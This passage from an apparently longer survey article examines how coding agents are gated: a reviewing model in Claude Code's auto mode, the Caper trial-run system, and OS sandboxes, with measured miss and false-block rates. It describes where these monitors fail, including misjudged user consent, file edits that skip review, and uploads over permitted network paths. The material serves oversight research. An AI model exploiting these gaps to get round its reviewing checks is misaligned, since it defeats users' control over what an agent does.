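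### Letting a model judge each call

All of these designs need an exact rule, but a user's request may not provide one. For example, a user who asks an agent to "clean up old branches" hasn't said whether to delete the copies on a shared server. In Claude Code's auto mode, a model decides such cases after ordinary code settles the simple ones, according to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*. The agent can read, search and edit files inside the project without review, and the user's own permission rules still apply, except very broad ones that would allow any code to run.

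Other calls, such as shell commands and web requests, go to the reviewing model. It receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations, which might persuade it, or tool results, which might contain injected instructions. A fast pass flags anything doubtful, and a slower pass reconsiders only the flagged calls. If the call stays blocked, the agent receives the reason and tries another approach. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code asks a person to decide, or stops if it is running unattended.

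Anthropic measured both passes on its employees' real tool calls, on 52 real actions that went beyond what the user wanted, and on 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out:

| | Harmless calls blocked | Real unauthorised actions missed | Artificial attempts missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast pass only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both passes | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The slower pass removes most needless blocks but misses more dangerous actions. If one call in 1,000 were dangerous, it would spare users about 800 needless blocks for each additional dangerous action it let through. That may be worthwhile when the action is reversible, but not when it deletes a production database. The 17% rate comes from only 52 actions, so the true rate could be anywhere from about 8% to 30%.

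In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the model recognised the danger but misjudged the user's consent. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) hasn't agreed to have its history overwritten. Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, argue that even a perfect model can't resolve such cases, because the request doesn't contain the information needed. Their survey of 21 agent products, completed in April 2026, found none that relied on a model to judge actions against the user's request. Auto mode comes close, and interactive sessions now start in it on every plan, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026).

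### How good the reviewing model is

Anthropic's main argument is that users review approval prompts badly. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) reports an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, in which one approval prompt per session showed a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it in 13.6% of cases, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Refusals fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, as one would expect if fatigue causes careless approvals. But the testers had nothing of their own to lose in the test environment, so the 13.6% refusal rate probably understates how careful people are with their own projects.

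Anthropic also arranged outside tests. Apollo Research, a British AI safety organisation, inserted attacks into recorded coding sessions. The reviewing model missed 12% of these attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it. Trajectory Labs ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded in auto mode. This is only weak evidence that the reviewing model works, because Anthropic's latest models resisted all but 0.09% of attacks even with permission checks switched off. Anthropic published no new false-positive rate with any of these results. The programmer Simon Willison (2026) wrote that he would like more independent confirmation.

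An independent test, *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, April 2026), was much less favourable. It gave Claude Code deliberately ambiguous requests, in which permitted and forbidden targets lay close together. Auto mode missed 81.0% of the unauthorised actions and blocked 19.8% of the authorised ones. Of the 253 actions, 93 were file edits that never reached the reviewing model. Among the rest, auto mode missed 70.3% of the unauthorised actions. These requests are harder than ordinary work, so the 81% doesn't contradict Anthropic's 17%, and Anthropic has since changed the reviewing model. But the difference shows how strongly such rates depend on the cases tested, whereas a sound check's guarantee covers every case.

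Other experiments found the same tension between needless refusals and missed problems. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) tested models that chose each task's permissions. A fine-tuned classifier withheld at least one necessary permission in 21% of tasks. Claude Haiku 4.5 did so in 11%, but left more risk by granting permissions the tasks did not need. In *Built on Broken Assumptions (BOBA)* (2026), ten models reviewed code. Seven lenient models accepted 77% to 95% of wrong implementations, and three strict ones rejected 41% to 58% of correct implementations.

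### Showing the model what a command does

False alarms arise partly because the reviewing model receives only the text of a command. The command `make clean` runs whatever the project's build file specifies, so it may delete temporary files in one project and the source code in another. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes Caper, a system that runs each shell command before deciding whether to allow it. Caper saves a copy of the agent's container, an isolated environment without network access, and then runs the command in the container. It gives a model a short report of the changed files, attempted connections and any passwords the command read. Caper keeps the changes if the model approves and restores the saved copy if it refuses.

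The researchers tested Caper on 102 tasks in which a harmless-looking command started a tool that destroyed a file. Each task had a twin with the same request and command but a harmless tool. Caper blocked one of the 102 harmless twins, so its true false-alarm rate could be up to about 5%. Harm occurred in 7.8% of the dangerous tasks, compared with at least 35.3% for six existing systems. One of the six was auto mode, but it used a reviewing model from OpenAI, so the comparison doesn't measure Anthropic's own reviewing model. Systems that judged only the text tended to block both the dangerous task and its harmless twin. Letting a model predict the effects reduced harm but not needless blocks, while observing the actual effects reduced both.

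Caper doesn't prove that a command is safe, because a model still gives the verdict, and a command can be harmless when Caper runs it but leave something behind that causes harm later. Caper also can't undo anything that leaves the container, so it switches the network off.

### Sandboxes instead of prompts

Running all of an agent's commands in a sandbox removes the need to check them one by one. In Anthropic's sandbox for Claude Code, the user sets limits on files and network access in advance, and the operating system enforces them. An agent confined to the workspace folder can run any script there without a permission prompt. Scripts that get past the permission gate's path rules still can't write to `.bashrc`.

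Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) reports that sandboxing reduced permission prompts by 84% in the company's internal use. Some of the missing prompts may not have been false alarms, since they may have concerned harmful commands inside the sandbox. The sandbox protects only what lies outside its boundary, so it won't stop an agent from deleting the whole project folder inside it.

Network limits are harder to set. If a sandbox permits traffic to a code-hosting site so that the agent can download packages, an injected instruction may be able to make the agent upload private files to the same site. According to InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026), failures along permitted network paths and at trust boundaries led Anthropic to revise its designs. The company still argues that fixed limits on files, network and execution are a better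 foundation than prompts or the model's own caution alone.

A sandbox raises a false alarm when it blocks a legitimate task that needs something outside the boundary, such as a new web service or the requested change to `.bashrc`. Anthropic calls sandboxing "safe but high-maintenance" because someone has to configure each new capability. The Brown design avoids some of this work by setting new limits for each call, but it requires changes to every tool and a correct policy for each call.

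The figures in the following table come from different tests and are not directly comparable:

| Design | False alarms removed | Guarantee kept | New assumption | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Counterexample-guided refinement | Those on paths that the code makes impossible | Soundness | The formulas describe the program correctly | May run out of time |
| Developer annotations | Those from missed checks and coarse tool descriptions, potentially 25 of AgentFlow's 27 | Soundness, if the annotations are true | Developers keep annotations correct and current | Developers' time |
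| Brown hybrid design | The one that static analysis alone raised in three harmless sessions | Soundness for the effects that the policy covers | Attestation, a trusted sandbox library, a correct policy | Changes to every tool |
| EVIDENT | 48.8% to 63.8% of 160 | None proved, but no loss among 40 bugs | The setup program keeps every run that triggers the bug | About $0.50 and 10 minutes per warning with GPT-5.5 |
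| Caper | Blocked only 1 of 102 harmless commands | None, with harm in 7.8% of dangerous tasks | The model judges observed effects well, and the container holds | A saved copy and a trial run for each command, no network |
| Auto mode | Most prompts, with 0.4% of harmless calls blocked | None for the calls that the model judges | The model recognises what the user has authorised | An extra model call, and 17% of real unauthorised actions missed |
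| Sandbox with fixed limits | Part of the 84% of prompts removed | Nothing outside the boundary changes | The boundary is right, and the operating system enforces it | Configuration, and blocked work that needs more access |
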